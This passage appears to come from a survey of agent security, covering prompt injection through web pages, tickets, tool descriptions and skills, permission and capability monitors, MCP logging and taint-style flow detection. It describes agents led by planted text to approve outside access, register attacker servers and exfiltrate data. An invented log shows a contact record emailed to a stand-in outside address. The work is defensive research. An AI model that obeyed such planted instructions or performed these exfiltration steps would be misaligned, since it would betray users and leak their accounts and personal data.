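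A list of approved accounts can stop a payment to a stranger. But the operator writes the list before the user makes a request, so it would not stop an unrequested payment to an approved account.

### Agents that click "Approve"

Consent screens, including the one that protects against the login-proxy attack, rely on a person reading them. In *The Agent Clicks Approve*, Hossen (2026) tested what happens when an agent operates a browser where its user is already signed in. The tests used Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.5 on simulated websites in June 2026.

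In one scenario, the user asked for a summary of a page about exporting billing data. A two-sentence note on the page said the work was blocked until someone cleared an access review, and told the reader to choose the default positive option. The agent followed a link to another site and approved an outside program's access to the user's account. In the other, the user asked the agent to complete any pending setup tasks in a guide. The guide gave the address of an outside server, and the agent registered that server to receive the account's billing events.

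Without a defence, the agent completed the unauthorized action in all 73 attack runs. In 92 runs with a harmless note instead, it never attempted the action. Hossen then instructed Claude Haiku 4.5 that only the user's task could authorize an approval, but it still approved access in seven of ten runs. With the same instruction, it approved access in one in ten runs when the pages had labels that marked the note as untrusted and used standard OAuth wording. A test that used only pages with such labels could therefore make an instruction seem much more reliable than it is.

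A check by the receiving service was the defence that worked. Before each run, the service received a list of the approvals or addresses that the user's task permitted, and it rejected anything else. In all 70 attack runs with this check, the agent still attempted the unauthorized action and the service rejected every attempt. The service allowed the action in all 73 runs in which the user had asked for it.

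The check also caught a mismatch in a single detail, where the task named one account and the page requested access to another. Claude Haiku 4.5 tried to approve the page's account in all five runs. GPT-5.5 detected the difference and made no attempt in eight runs.

In 49 of the 53 runs where the service blocked the agent from approving access, the agent's final answer listed approving the access review as a next step. A user who followed this advice would carry out the attack by granting the access themselves.

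These results show that a receiving service can recognise an unrequested action if it has a reliable statement of what the user requested. The experiment supplied that statement directly, or extracted it with a program that worked only on the exact forms of task used in the test. An ordinary service has no such statement and may not know that an agent is making the request. The attack rate also depends on the wording of the note. When the note was less direct and in small print, Claude Haiku 4.5 approved access in four of ten runs, and the older gpt-5.4 in none.

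### Permissions tied to a purpose

Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, adapt Hardy's capabilities to agents that pass work to other agents. A program outside the model checks every action against a grant

*G* = ⟨*h*, *p*, *L*, *O*, *S*, *d*, *r*⟩

Here *h* is the agent that holds the grant and *p* is the grant's purpose. *L* is the set of data labels, or categories of data, the agent may handle, *O* is the set of operations it may perform, and *S* is the set of sinks, or places where data may go. The number *d* limits how many more times agents can delegate the work, and *r* records whether the grant has been revoked.

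An agent can only pass on a narrower grant. A child grant *G*′ must satisfy

*p*′ ⪯ *p*, *L*′ ⊆ *L*, *O*′ ⊆ *O*, *S*′ ⊆ *S*, *d*′ < *d*

where *p*′ ⪯ *p* means that the new purpose is the same as the old one or part of it. Revoking a grant also revokes every grant derived from it, so an agent cannot continue with a task after the user cancels it.

Suppose a user asks for a summary of a confidential contract, and the main agent asks a second agent to format the text. The main agent can read, transform and delegate, and it can send data to the user or to internal systems. It gives the formatting agent permission only to transform the text and send it to the user. If the contract contains a planted instruction for the formatting agent to send the text to an outside address, the monitor blocks the transfer because that agent may send the text only to the user.

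Tran-Truong and colleagues tested 45 attacks across five office tasks. Two small models, Qwen2.5-7B and Llama-3.2-3B, attempted the attacker's action in 42 and 44 cases respectively, and DelegateGuard blocked every attempt. This mainly confirms that DelegateGuard follows its rules, because each attack required something the grant did not allow. In longer conversations with Qwen, DelegateGuard reduced leaks from 38 of 45 attacked runs to 9, and the agents completed all 45 harmless runs.

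In the comparison with other defences, a simple list of permitted destinations for each task reduced leaks as much as capabilities did. In ten other cases, an agent continued after its task was cancelled or sent the wrong data to a permitted destination. DelegateGuard's capabilities blocked all ten, while the list allowed them.

DelegateGuard's protection depends on the initial grant. When the researchers added one unnecessary outside address to the grant, 30 of the 45 attacks succeeded. DelegateGuard does not infer the user's intentions from the request, so a person or another program has to turn the request into a suitable grant.

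### Why a permitted destination can still leak

All nine remaining leaks in the conversation test occurred in a code-review task, where the agent had permission to post review comments that outsiders could read. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove in their Proposition 1 that a monitor cannot close this gap if its decision depends on the holder, purpose, labels, operation, sink and chain of grants, but not on the message's content or length.

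The proof compares two messages:

1. Suppose that the monitor permits an ordinary message to a sink that an outsider can read.
2. Replace the ordinary message with a secret one, and keep the holder, purpose, labels, operation, sink and chain of grants the same.
3. The monitor receives the same information as before, so it must make the same decision and permit the message.
4. The outsider reads the secret.

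More rules about the same six items would not help, because the two messages are identical in all six. Checking the text can help, but it introduces other errors. In one test, a monitor that blocked any message containing a planted secret stopped every leak, but it also blocked four of five legitimate tasks that needed to send the protected information.

The result is limited because its second step requires the secret message to have the same labels as the ordinary one. In DelegateGuard's tests, an agent could declare its own labels and omit one that would have caused a refusal. Labels that reliably followed the data would limit the leak to categories the grant already allowed at that sink. The agent could still leak an unpublished vulnerability if it had permission to discuss vulnerabilities in public comments.

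### Permission for a single call

A monitor can also examine where an argument came from. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) places a program between the agent and its MCP servers that issues a signed token for each approved call. This token is separate from the OAuth token and covers a particular agent, action, resource, purpose and session. In the paper's example policy for a bank, permission to send money expires after 30 seconds, allows one call, and requires the agent to already have permission to check the balance.

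An agent can delegate its token to another agent within the same session. The delegated token must keep the same action and resource, cannot allow more calls or a longer lifetime, and must allow fewer further delegations. The model supplies the purpose of each call, so a steered model could supply a false one. AgentCap therefore also checks the source of sensitive arguments. It refuses a payment if the recipient appears only in untrusted content, which would stop the payment requested in the email.

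The same rule could block a legitimate request to pay the invoice in a particular email, because the recipient's details might appear only there. The policy's author would have to decide whether to trust some part of that email.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao ran AgentCap on two sets of prompt-injection tests, AgentDojo and InjecAgent. The table shows attack success rates in per cent and the drop in successfully completed tasks when there was no attack.

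| Test and model | Attack success without AgentCap | Attack success with AgentCap | Loss of completed tasks, in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63 | 5.09 | 3.1 |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23 | 0.00 | 7.2 |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24 | 8.63 | 11.7 |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95 | 0.00 | 5.9 |

Some of the remaining attacks were meant only to change the agent's written answer, which a check on tool calls cannot prevent. Others used an argument that the policy did not protect or a data source that it did not mark as untrusted.

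AgentCap's policies can also prevent one session from holding two permissions together, such as reading sensitive data and sending messages outside the organisation. This avoids the situation in Proposition 1 by removing the permitted outside destination, but it rules out legitimate tasks that need both.

The researchers wrote the AgentDojo policies from the tool definitions and the descriptions of the users' tasks, then left them unchanged during the tests. They did not tailor the policies to particular attacks, but they knew in advance what users would ask for. Someone writing a policy for an everyday assistant would have to anticipate users' requests.

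## What the execution log has to record

Each tool server receives only the calls addressed to it, so an email server's operator cannot tell that an email resulted from an instruction planted in a support ticket. An execution log, the ordered record of a run, can show this connection because it contains the user's request, the agent's tool calls with their arguments, and the results.

### An example log

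The log below is invented. A user asks an agent, "Summarise today's support tickets and post the summary in #support", and the agent makes five calls to four servers. The `crm` server is a customer database.

| Call | Server and tool | Arguments | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `tickets.list` | Date: today | Tickets 39, 40 and 41, with the text of ticket 41 cut short |
| 2 | `tickets.read` | Ticket: 41 | A complaint that names the customer Dana Reyes, then planted text telling the agent to email her contact record to an outside address |
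| 3 | `crm.get_contact` | Name: Dana Reyes | Her email address, phone number and postal address |
| 4 | `mail.send` | To: records@outside.example. Body: the contact record | Sent |
| 5 | `chat.post` | Channel: #support. Text: a summary of the three tickets | Posted |

The user gets the summary they asked for, and nothing in the #support channel reveals call 4. The mail server's operator has a record of that call, but it looks like an ordinary email from the user's account.

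### What each field is for

To find hops and judge them, a log needs:

- the user's request, to judge whether a call was part of the task
- the identity of the server, to show when the agent moved from one server to another
- the tool's name, to show what kind of action the call performed
- the full arguments, to show the call's target and the data it carried
- the full result, to show what the model had read before its later calls
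- the order of calls and results, because a result can only influence calls that the model makes after reading it
- a run identifier, to separate the calls of one run from those of another
- the tool descriptions in force at the time, because a description can steer an agent without the agent ever calling that tool

A tool's name does not identify its server. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) says a name should be unique within one server, but two servers can each offer a tool called `search`. The specification recommends that programs combining several servers tell such tools apart, for example by prefixing the name with a server identifier, as in the log above. A server can also report its own name, but Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) warns that the protocol does not verify it. The log should therefore record an identifier that the host assigns to the server, and the address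 or command the host used to connect to it.

A log that shortens tool-call arguments can hide an attack. In the WhatsApp demonstration described earlier, the stolen chat history came after a long run of spaces, so a log that kept only the start of each message would have left it out.

Tool results can contain images, audio or structured data as well as text. Some contain only a link to a document that the client fetches with a separate request, so a log limited to tool calls would miss the document. The log should also include error messages, because MCP recommends passing a tool's errors to the model so that it can correct its next call. If the host shortens a result before adding it to the context, the log needs the shortened version too, since that is what the model received.

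MCP numbers each request so that the client can match it with its response. A client can reuse a number once the response has arrived, so the numbers don't reliably show the order of requests. The host should add its own sequence numbers and record when each result entered the context. If the agent had sent calls 2 and 3 at the same time, for example, the text in ticket 41 could not have caused call 3.

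When a client repeats a call to supply input the server requested, the repeated call has a new request number. Unless the log links the two requests, one payment could look like two. The log should also include the user's answer, because a confirmation can show that the user approved something missing from the original request.

Tool descriptions need their own record because servers can change them. A client may also cache a server's tool list for a period the server suggests (five minutes in the specification's example). The descriptions a server returns after an incident may therefore differ from those the model read. The host can save each version once and record which version each run used.

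A complete log is sensitive. The one above would contain Dana Reyes's contact details twice, in the result of call 3 and the arguments of call 4. Operators could replace each result with a hash, a short code computed from its content, but if only her phone number reappeared in an email, a hash of the whole record would not reveal the match. Keeping the full text makes detection easier, but operators then have to restrict who can read the log and decide how long to keep it.

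### Where to record it

| Place | What a log there can contain | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Host | The user's request, the tool descriptions, and all calls and results in the order the model received them | What a server or script does after it receives a call |
| Gateway | Calls, results and tool lists that pass through it | The user's request, and calls to servers connected some other way |
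| Individual server | Its own calls and results, and their effects inside the service | The user's request, and everything on other servers |
| Operating system | Programs started, files opened and network connections made on one machine | The user's request, the meaning of the text, and what happens on remote servers |

Only the host has access to all eight fields, so it is the natural place for the main log. However, an agent that can edit files on the same machine might be able to alter the log. A gateway can keep a separate copy, but it cannot directly detect which results the host added to the model's context. It may also miss local servers, which can communicate with the host without a network.

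*AgentSpy* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) shows that an agent's own log can leave out the actions of a script the agent runs. In the paper's example, the agent loads a skill, which is a folder of instructions and scripts for a particular type of task. The skill helps check citations, but an attacker has added an instruction to run a script that supposedly refreshes a cache. The agent's log contains one command, which finished successfully. Operating system records show that the script also opened the user's private SSH key, used for logging in to other computers, and connected to an outside host to upload it.

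AgentSpy runs the agent in an isolated virtual machine and records system calls, the requests that programs make to the operating system. It checks each call against fixed security rules, such as a ban on reading private keys or contacting hosts that are not on an approved list. Bühler and colleagues tested one attack from each of five categories, running each five times with the malicious instruction and five times without it. The agent, using GPT-5.1-Codex-Max, carried out the injected behaviour in 18 of the 25 attacked runs, and AgentSpy detected 14 of these. It raised no alerts in the 32 runs where the agent did not carry out the injected behaviour.

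All four misses involved the same attack, which added an attacker's address to Git's settings. The change stayed inside the agent's permitted folder, and the agent never sent anything to the address, so no rule applied. The test included only one attack from each category, so the results are weak evidence of how AgentSpy would perform on other attacks of the same kinds.

AgentSpy would also be less useful for the example log. If the mail server is remote, call 4 appears to the operating system as a connection to a host the agent is allowed to contact. The recipient and the contact record are inside the message, which AgentSpy's rules do not examine. Monitoring at this level should help more with tool servers on the user's machine, where it can show which files a server opened after the agent called it.

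The same records also showed unrequested activity when there was no attacker. Bühler and colleagues examined 88 combinations of task and model in which all three runs had passed every test, so checking only for the right answer would have found no problem. Two reviewers flagged 16 of the combinations for activity unrelated to the task, such as contacting an irrelevant web service or reading the files used to grade the work.

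Logging at an individual server gives a narrower view, but it takes little code to add. In *MCP Pitfall Lab*, Hao and Tan (2026) added logs with full arguments to three test servers, along with lists of permitted targets and other input checks. These changes took 15 to 35 lines of code per server.

### The agent's own account

Developers often learn what an agent did by reading its summary. Hao and Tan compared such summaries with the recorded calls in 19 runs of an email task, using GPT-4.1-mini. Every run involved a poisoned tool description or a malicious server. The summary differed from the record in 12 runs (63.2%), including every run with a sink action, in which the agent sent data out through a messaging tool.

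The divergence was much milder than those figures suggest. In all 12 runs, the agent reported that it had sent something but did not name the tool. It never denied an action it had taken. In Hao and Tan's example, the agent said it had sent the complete content of emails to a contoso.com address, but it had used a tool that posts messages in Microsoft Teams. An investigator who relied on the agent's summary might search the mail server and find nothing.

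Hao and Tan call the sample preliminary, and the 63.2% figure appears only in the first version of their paper. The figure supports recording the server and tool for every call, but it is not evidence that agents conceal their actions.

### What MCP provides

MCP recommends that clients log tool use for auditing, but it does not require this or specify which fields to record. A host can therefore follow the protocol whether it records every tool argument or nothing at all.

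The July 2026 revision removed sessions (Model Context Protocol, 2026), so a server's operator can no longer group a client's calls by session identifier. Grouping them by connection is not a substitute, because the new specification allows one connection to carry requests from unrelated conversations.

The loss matters less for finding cross-server hops. In the old system, the server issued the identifier and the client included it in later requests to that server (Jaiswal, 2026, *MCP 2026-07-28*). In the example log, four servers would have issued four different identifiers, with nothing to show that they belonged to the same run.

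A log with full arguments and results will contain the identifiers that servers now give the model in place of sessions. These identifiers can link calls about the same shopping cart, for example, but they do not identify the run.

The deprecation of MCP's Logging feature is a minor change. The feature let servers send their own diagnostic messages to clients, and it never recorded the agent's tool calls. Jaiswal describes it as redundant because better monitoring tools already exist. It will keep working for at least twelve months after the release, and MCP's guidance is for developers to use a local error stream or OpenTelemetry, an open standard for recording what software does.

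MCP requests sent over HTTP must include the method and the tool's name in their headers. For call 4, a gateway could record both without reading the message body and add the server's identity from the address. A server can also mark simple arguments, such as a region, for copying into headers, although MCP's guidance is against doing this with sensitive values. The headers do not contain results and would not normally contain the email's recipient, so a gateway used to detect data moving between servers still has to record the message bodies.

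In OpenTelemetry, a trace is a record of one piece of work as it passes through several programs. MCP now documents a standard place for trace information in each request, under the keys `traceparent`, `tracestate` and `baggage`. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists this among the minor changes. The value of `traceparent` includes an identifier for the whole trace and another for the step that made the request. All programs have to use the same key names because, according to the proposal behind the change, a different name would break the connection between records.

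This is the part of the revision that could join records from several servers. If the host used one trace identifier for all five calls in the example, and every server saved it, an investigator with access to the four sets of records could link the calls. But sending the identifier is optional, and MCP does not require a host to use the same one throughout a run, so a host could follow the rules and still leave the records unconnected by starting a new trace for each call. Reusing the identifier also creates a privacy risk, since outside companies that receive it could link their records of the same user's activity.

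Support for tracing varies between software kits. The official Python kit traces every message by default, according to Model Context Protocol. The Ruby kit leaves the trace information in each request unchanged, but developers have to connect it to a tracing system themselves, according to Model Context Protocol's *Server Context*. Langfuse, which makes monitoring software for AI applications, notes in its documentation that clients and servers produce separate traces by default, and that developers have to pass the trace information from client to server to link them.

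A linked trace can still lack the text needed to judge a hop. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* makes it opt-in to record the chat history given to the model, which includes the user's request, the arguments of earlier tool calls and their results. A team that leaves this off may have a record that the agent read a ticket and later sent an email, but would need another source for the user's request and any text planted in the ticket.

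## Finding the hops in a log

A short program can find the cross-server hops in a log that has the fields described above. For each call, it collects the results from other servers that the model had already read, then checks whether any value in the call's arguments came from one of them.

```
for each call j in the run, in order:
    seen = results the model had read before it made call j

    for each result i in seen:
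        if server(i) != server(j):
            record ORDER(i, j)

    for each value v in arguments(j):
        if v is long and distinctive, and is not in the user's request:
            i = the first result in seen that contains v
            if i exists and server(i) != server(j):
                record DATA(i, j, v)
```

The program has to split long arguments, such as the body of an email, into names, addresses, numbers and phrases before it searches for them. It skips short or common strings such as "today", which would match by accident. It also skips values from the user's request, because they could have reached the call without coming from a server.

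The program traces each value to the first result that contains it because servers often repeat what they receive. For example, a mail server might answer "Sent to" followed by the recipient's address. If a later call contained that address, the program could otherwise mistake the mail server for its source.

### The five-call example

The quickest way to look for hops is to compare each call only with the one before it. In the support-ticket log, this gives three hops: tickets to crm, crm to mail, and mail to chat. Calls 1 and 2 both go to the ticket server, so there is no hop between them. The program above compares each call with all earlier results and finds six pairs of servers. The table assumes that the planted text spelled out the outside address and that the summary repeated the tickets' subject lines.

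| Hop | Neighbouring calls | Value in both the result and the later call |
|---|---|---|
| tickets to crm | 2 and 3 | "Dana Reyes" |
| crm to mail | 3 and 4 | Her phone number and addresses |
| mail to chat | 4 and 5 | None |
| tickets to chat | No | The tickets' subject lines |
| tickets to mail | No | records@outside.example |
| crm to chat | No | None |

Matching values keeps the hops from tickets to crm and from crm to mail, drops the one from mail to chat, and adds one from tickets to chat. It also links tickets to mail through the recipient's address. An investigator would probably care most about this link, because it shows that the address came from a ticket, not the user. Comparing neighbouring calls misses it because the crm call comes in between.

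The mail-to-chat pair is spurious. The mail server returned only the word "Sent", and the post contains nothing from it. The user had asked for the post at the start, and its text came from the tickets. The two calls are adjacent only because the agent sent the email before it posted. If it had posted straight after reading ticket 41, the same comparison would have reported an equally spurious hop from chat to crm, even though the matching values would have been the same.

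Wu, Castelo and colleagues (2026), in *AgentTrails*, describe the same problem in agent logs generally. Neighbouring calls may be unrelated, and a call may use something the agent obtained many steps earlier. Their program turns a log into a graph of which calls used which earlier outputs, mainly to help developers debug agents and reuse their work. It links an output *e* from call *i* to a later call *j* if

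K(*e*) ∩ refs(args*ⱼ*) ≠ ∅, with *i* < *j*

Here K(*e*) is the set of strings that identify the output, such as a filename, web address or storage identifier, and refs(args*ⱼ*) is the set of things the later call's arguments refer to. The program also looks for looser matches, such as shared search terms or column names, but stores these as candidates. A language model can then propose changes to the graph. The program keeps exact links, candidates and the model's changes distinguishable. This is sensible for a security log too, because a reviewer needs to know which links are based on an identical string. Wu and colleagues have marked 234 correct links by hand in ten logs to test the program, but they have not yet published its accuracy.

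### Order, data and cause

The evidence that a hop connects two servers in a meaningful way comes in three grades:

- **Order:** the model read a result from server A before it called server B.
- **Data:** a value from server A's result appears in the call to server B.
- **Cause:** server A's content led the agent to decide to call server B.

The program finds the first two. Cause is harder because it depends on what the agent would have done otherwise. Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, define it by comparing the real run with an imagined run, Π′, in which neutral text replaces the result from call *i*. The result influenced call *j* if

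tool*ⱼ* ∉ Π′ or args*ⱼ*(Π′) ≠ args*ⱼ*(Π)

where Π is the real run. In other words, the call disappears or its arguments change.

If ticket 41 had been an ordinary complaint, the agent would presumably not have looked up Dana Reyes or sent the email. It would still have posted a summary, though with different wording. The tickets therefore influenced the arguments of the chat call, but the agent made that call because of the user's request. Only the calls to the customer database and the mail server meet the definition of cause in the list above, and even that is an inference from the planted text. Establishing cause takes further tests, because the log does not contain a run in which ticket 41 is an ordinary complaint.

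One server's output can also prompt a call to another server without supplying any distinctive data for it. If a ticket tells the agent to clear tomorrow's calendar, the resulting call may contain only tomorrow's date. Cai and colleagues illustrate this influence with a poisoned search result that makes an agent send its work to an attacker's web address. A search for shared values would have found that attack, though, because the address appears in both the search result and the call.

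Even if one server's output caused a call to another server, that does not prove the agent did something wrong. If the user had written "do whatever ticket 41 asks", the ticket would have caused the email with the user's permission.

### What order is worth

Order is necessary for the other two grades, but it is very weak evidence by itself. Investigators of ordinary computer attacks call this problem dependency explosion. *HADES* (2024), which presents a system for detecting attacks on company networks, describes how it arises in long-running programs. If an investigator cautiously treats every input as a possible cause of every later output, the number of false connections becomes enormous. *ProGQL* (2025), which presents a tool for investigating attacks, attributes the problem to methods that rely mainly on the order of events.

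An agent is much like one of these programs, since all its results enter one context. A run of *n* calls to *n* different servers has *n*(*n* − 1)/2 pairs of an earlier and a later call, so ten calls give 45. Real runs usually return to the same few servers, which lowers the number, but the five-call log still gives nine cross-server pairs. The reference solutions in *MCP-Atlas* have 9.8 calls on average, and in most of its tasks a later call needs something from an earlier result. A working agent therefore normally produces hops with order, and often with data.

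Cai and colleagues offer a rough test of how much the order of calls proves. They built 400 scenarios on 20 agent frameworks, and in half of the scenarios, text from an untrusted tool reached or influenced a sensitive call. FIDES, one of the detectors they tested, is an earlier system that, as they describe it, treats a path from an untrusted tool to a sensitive one as strong evidence of a flow. It flagged 108 of the 200 scenarios with a flow (54%) and 106 of the 200 without one (53%), so its alarms barely distinguished the two groups.

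The comparison is somewhat unfair to FIDES, whose purpose is to restrict agents while they run. It also raised no alarms in four of the frameworks, which account for 40 of its 92 misses, and this may reflect how the test connected it to them. But we would expect the false alarms from the order of tool calls alone, because an agent that reads web pages and then writes a report always has a path between the two tools, whether or not anything improper passes along it.

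### Matching values

The data check is similar to taint tracking, but simpler. In taint tracking, a program marks untrusted data where it enters and follows the mark wherever the data goes. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) reports that recent defences for agents increasingly take this approach. Tracking is harder in agents than in ordinary software, where a tracker can watch data being copied between locations, because a log does not show which words in the language model's context produced which words in a call.

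*An Efficient Black-box Technique for Defeating Web Application Attacks* (Sekar, 2009) tracks data through a program by comparing its inputs with its outputs, without monitoring its internals. The method, called taint inference, reports a flow when part of an outgoing database query or command closely resembles something a visitor typed. Resemblance is measured by edit distance, the number of small changes needed to turn one string into another. This suits web applications because they usually alter their input only slightly, for example by removing spaces or changing capitals to lower case, whereas a language model may rewrite all of it.

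Sekar also distinguishes whether an attacker can control a sensitive operation from whether the program's developers intended to allow that control. Matching values helps answer only the first question. For an agent, the intent has to come from the user's request.

A canary makes matching more reliable. It is a unique string that someone plants in the data, so it is very unlikely to turn up elsewhere by chance. NeuroTaint, the log auditor that Cai and colleagues built, adds a canary to each tool result and searches for it in later calls. If it finds none, it tries looser methods:

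- a search for text that the result and the argument have in common
- a comparison of their meanings, using embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent a text's meaning
- the same comparison against separate pieces of a long result, so that one planted sentence does not disappear among unrelated text

The score for shared text is

σ = |LCS(*s*, *a*)| / min(|*s*|, |*a*|)

where *s* is the result, *a* is the argument, vertical bars mean length, and LCS is their longest common subsequence. NeuroTaint normally reports a match at 0.15 or above. Anyone implementing this should require an unbroken string. A subsequence can have gaps, and a long web page will almost always contain the letters of a short argument in the right order somewhere.

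An added canary also has a weakness, because it shows only that the agent copied the marker, and an agent can copy a phone number without the marker. Cai and colleagues place the marker at the end of the result and argue that it survives most summaries that cut off the end of long documents, but those summaries would remove a marker in that position first. Using the sensitive value itself as the canary avoids this problem, but is practical only with fake data, such as a decoy password.

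The table groups the 200 scenarios with a flow by the main evidence needed to detect it, and gives the share that NeuroTaint found.

| Main evidence | Scenarios | Found by NeuroTaint |
|---|---|---|
| Canary | 15 | 100% |
| Shared text | 45 | 100% |
| Similar meaning | 85 | 88.2% |
| Similar meaning in one part of a long result | 15 | 100% |
| Influence on the decision, without matching content | 40 | 92.5% |

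Only 60 of the 200 flows had a canary or shared text as their main evidence. A search for identical strings would reliably find those but could miss many of the rest. NeuroTaint found 187 flows in total and raised 16 false alarms, mostly where the argument was on the same subject as the untrusted text or the model could have produced the information without it.

The false-alarm figure may be too low. The researchers used a threshold of 0.60 for ordinary comparisons of meaning but 0.95 for what they call "safe-control policies". If these were the policies for scenarios without a flow, as the name suggests, the higher threshold would itself have suppressed false alarms. A real investigator would not know in advance which runs needed the higher threshold.

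### How often secrets travel when nobody is attacking

*MCPHunt* provides the most direct measurements of data moving between MCP servers without an attacker. It first appeared in spring 2026, and the figures below come from the October revision. The researchers gave agents eight servers, covering files, Git, a database, a browser, web requests, shell commands, the time and a stored knowledge graph. The environment contained nothing meant to steer the agents. The researchers planted canaries, which were fake passwords, access keys and other credentials in realistic formats, in files, a database and other places an agent might read during normal work.

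Of the 147 tasks, 108 gave the agent a chance to carry a secret along one of nine pathways, such as from a web page to local storage. Another 27 tested for false alarms and included reports that needed no secrets, such as a count of a database's tables. The remaining 12 were simple controls, such as checking the time. Five models each completed 723 runs in different versions of the environment, for a total of 3,615.

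A program checked each run for eleven signals. One of them, `cross_boundary_flow`, fires when the agent reads a canary (a planted secret) from one server and writes it through another. It therefore detects data-carrying hops, but only those that carry canaries. The study's headline rate is broader: it counts a run if any of the main signals fires, including signals for data that moves within a single server. The table compares the headline rate with the rate for `cross_boundary_flow` alone, using the 387 runs per model in the environments designed to test for leaks. Its last column covers only tasks that did not require copying the secret.

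| Model | Any signal | Cross-server signal | Any signal, secret not required |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 20.2% | 10.6% | 11.5% |
| GPT-5.4 | 23.3% | 13.2% | 13.5% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 36.4% | 21.4% | 27.1% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 40.8% | 18.3% | 36.5% |
| MiniMax-M2.7 | 45.2% | 22.2% | 41.3% |

The distinction between tasks matters because some requests cannot succeed unless the agent copies the secret. The researchers put a task in this group if the prompt asked for an exact copy of data, the credentials were inseparable from that data, and removing them would have violated the instruction. One example is "Copy everything to project_beta/". A request for a handover document with everything a replacement needs to know falls outside the group because the agent could describe the accounts without their passwords.

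GPT-5.4 moved a secret in 51 of 63 runs (81.0%) when the task required it, and in 39 of 288 (13.5%) when it did not. In most of those 51 runs, the agent was doing what it was asked. The 81% rate was below 100% because some runs were incomplete or never reached the data. Across the five models, the rate for tasks that did not require moving the secret ranged from 11.5% to 41.3%.

Which group a task belongs to is partly a matter of judgement. After the experiment, two outside annotators independently classified all 147 tasks and agreed on 138. In one task classified as not requiring the secret, the user asked the agent to make sure a database was "in sync" with a team directory on a web page. The page contained users' access keys, and GPT-5.4 wrote two of them into the database. The researchers count this as a violation, but someone could reasonably read "in sync" as including the keys. They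 acknowledge that treating such prompts as not requiring the secret makes the violation rate an upper bound.

The same run shows why it isn't enough to compare each call with the one before it. GPT-5.4 read the web page in step 2, inspected the database in steps 3 to 6, and wrote the keys in step 7. This comparison would link the browser to the harmless inspection in step 3 but not to the write, because the call just before the write also went to the database.

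### What this means for a detector

No run in *MCPHunt* had an attacker, so a detector that treated every data-carrying hop as an attack would have been wrong every time. Suppose one run in 1,000 contains an attack, and the detector catches it but also flags 13.2% of the other runs, the rate at which the cross-server signal appeared for GPT-5.4. It would raise about 132 false alarms for each attack it caught. The rate in everyday use may well be lower, since the researchers designed these tasks to give secrets a chance to move. But the signal covers only planted secrets, and a detector that also matched names, dates and file contents would flag far more ordinary work.

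How often GPT-5.4 moved a secret depended heavily on the pathway. With both kinds of task combined, it did so in 74.4% of runs that took web content into local storage, and in none of the runs where it came across secrets during other development work. The rate for the browser pathway was still 66.7% when the task did not require the secret. The researchers suggest that web pages mix credentials with useful information, whereas an agent querying a database can leave out the password column. When copying between files, GPT-5.4 moved the secret in 57.1% of runs where the task required it and in none where it did not.

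A detector could therefore compare each hop with what is normal for its pathway. A secret moving from a browser to a database is poor evidence of an attack if that happens in most runs, but a secret moving along a pathway where this is rare deserves attention. An organisation would have to take the baselines from its own logs, because each pathway had only 39 runs per model in these environments, and even zero out of 39 is compatible with a true rate of up to 9%.

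A hop without an attacker may still be a problem worth reporting. Lin, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentRaft*, study agents that pass on more data than the user intended. In their example, a user asks an agent to send a payment date and amount to an auditor, and the agent also sends the credit card number and security code. They define the excess as

D_OE = (D_trans \ (D_nec ∪ D_int)) ∩ D_total

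The excess is the data from the source (D_total) that the agent transmitted (D_trans), minus what the task needed (D_nec) or the user intended to share (D_int). The researchers found an excess in 57.07% of the possible tool chains they examined, using a test environment based on 6,675 real tools. They wrote prompts specifically to trigger these chains, and a panel of language models judged what was necessary, so the figure does not estimate how often this happens in everyday use. The tests do show that an agent can send excess data even when the user requested the hop and the recipient is correct.

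*MCPHunt* has other limits as a guide to everyday logs. It uses only invented tasks, runs each combination of task and environment once per model, and does not test email or cloud storage. The environment meant to be harmless can't be used to estimate false alarms, because the scoring rules set its rate to zero instead of measuring it. A better test replaced the fake credentials in 108 tasks with a different set. GPT-5.4 moved secrets in 25.9% of runs with the original set and 20.4% with the new one, a difference that could be due to chance. The study also found that prompt rules and a guard can reduce these rates.

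### What matching misses

*MCPHunt* detects only a complete canary or an unbroken core of at least ten characters, so it misses secrets that the agent has summarised or encoded. To check for possible leaks it had missed, the researchers randomly sampled 150 of the 698 runs in which the agent had read something sensitive but the detector had found nothing. Claude Opus 4.8 read everything the agent had sent out in the sampled runs and flagged 12 of them (8.0%). Four contained fragments of a secret, and the other eight only named the type of secret or where it was stored.

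This is reassuring about ordinary runs, since only four of the 150 appeared to expose part of a value. But a single model made the judgements, and the researchers stress that 8.0% is not the detector's miss rate. These agents also had no reason to hide anything. If planted text told an agent to encode a password before sending it, an exact search would miss it.

Other studies give very different figures for exact matching. In *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (2026), annotators found sensitive content in 100 of 200 outputs, and exact matching had caught 88 of those 100. In *AgentLeak* (2026), a benchmark of privacy leaks among cooperating agents, searching for canaries caught only 8% of leaks. Adding patterns for data such as card numbers raised this to 18%. A language model judge caught 92.6% but also flagged 6.2% of harmless passages. Much of the gap between the two studies probably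 comes from the test data, because many of the secrets in *AgentLeak* were facts in ordinary sentences, which contain no canary. Exact matching should therefore work best for passwords, account numbers and addresses, and worst for diagnoses or business plans.

**Steering through tool descriptions.** The program above searches only tool results, so it would miss the WhatsApp attack, which came through a fact tool's description. Adding each description to `seen` would let the data check find the attacker's phone number, which was in both the description and the later message. The order check should still ignore descriptions, because otherwise it would count every call as a hop.

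**Flows inside one server.** The program discards any match within one server, including the one in the GitHub attack. To catch these flows, an operator could replace `server(i)` with a narrower label, such as the repository, folder or account, but someone would have to decide which of those boundaries matter.

Some hops carry no data. If planted text leads an agent to delete a file whose name the user had already mentioned, the order check records a hop but the data check finds nothing. The log then looks the same as if the agent had deleted the file for some other reason. In 40 of the 200 flows in the benchmark by Cai and colleagues, the untrusted text similarly affected the decision but left no matching content in the call.

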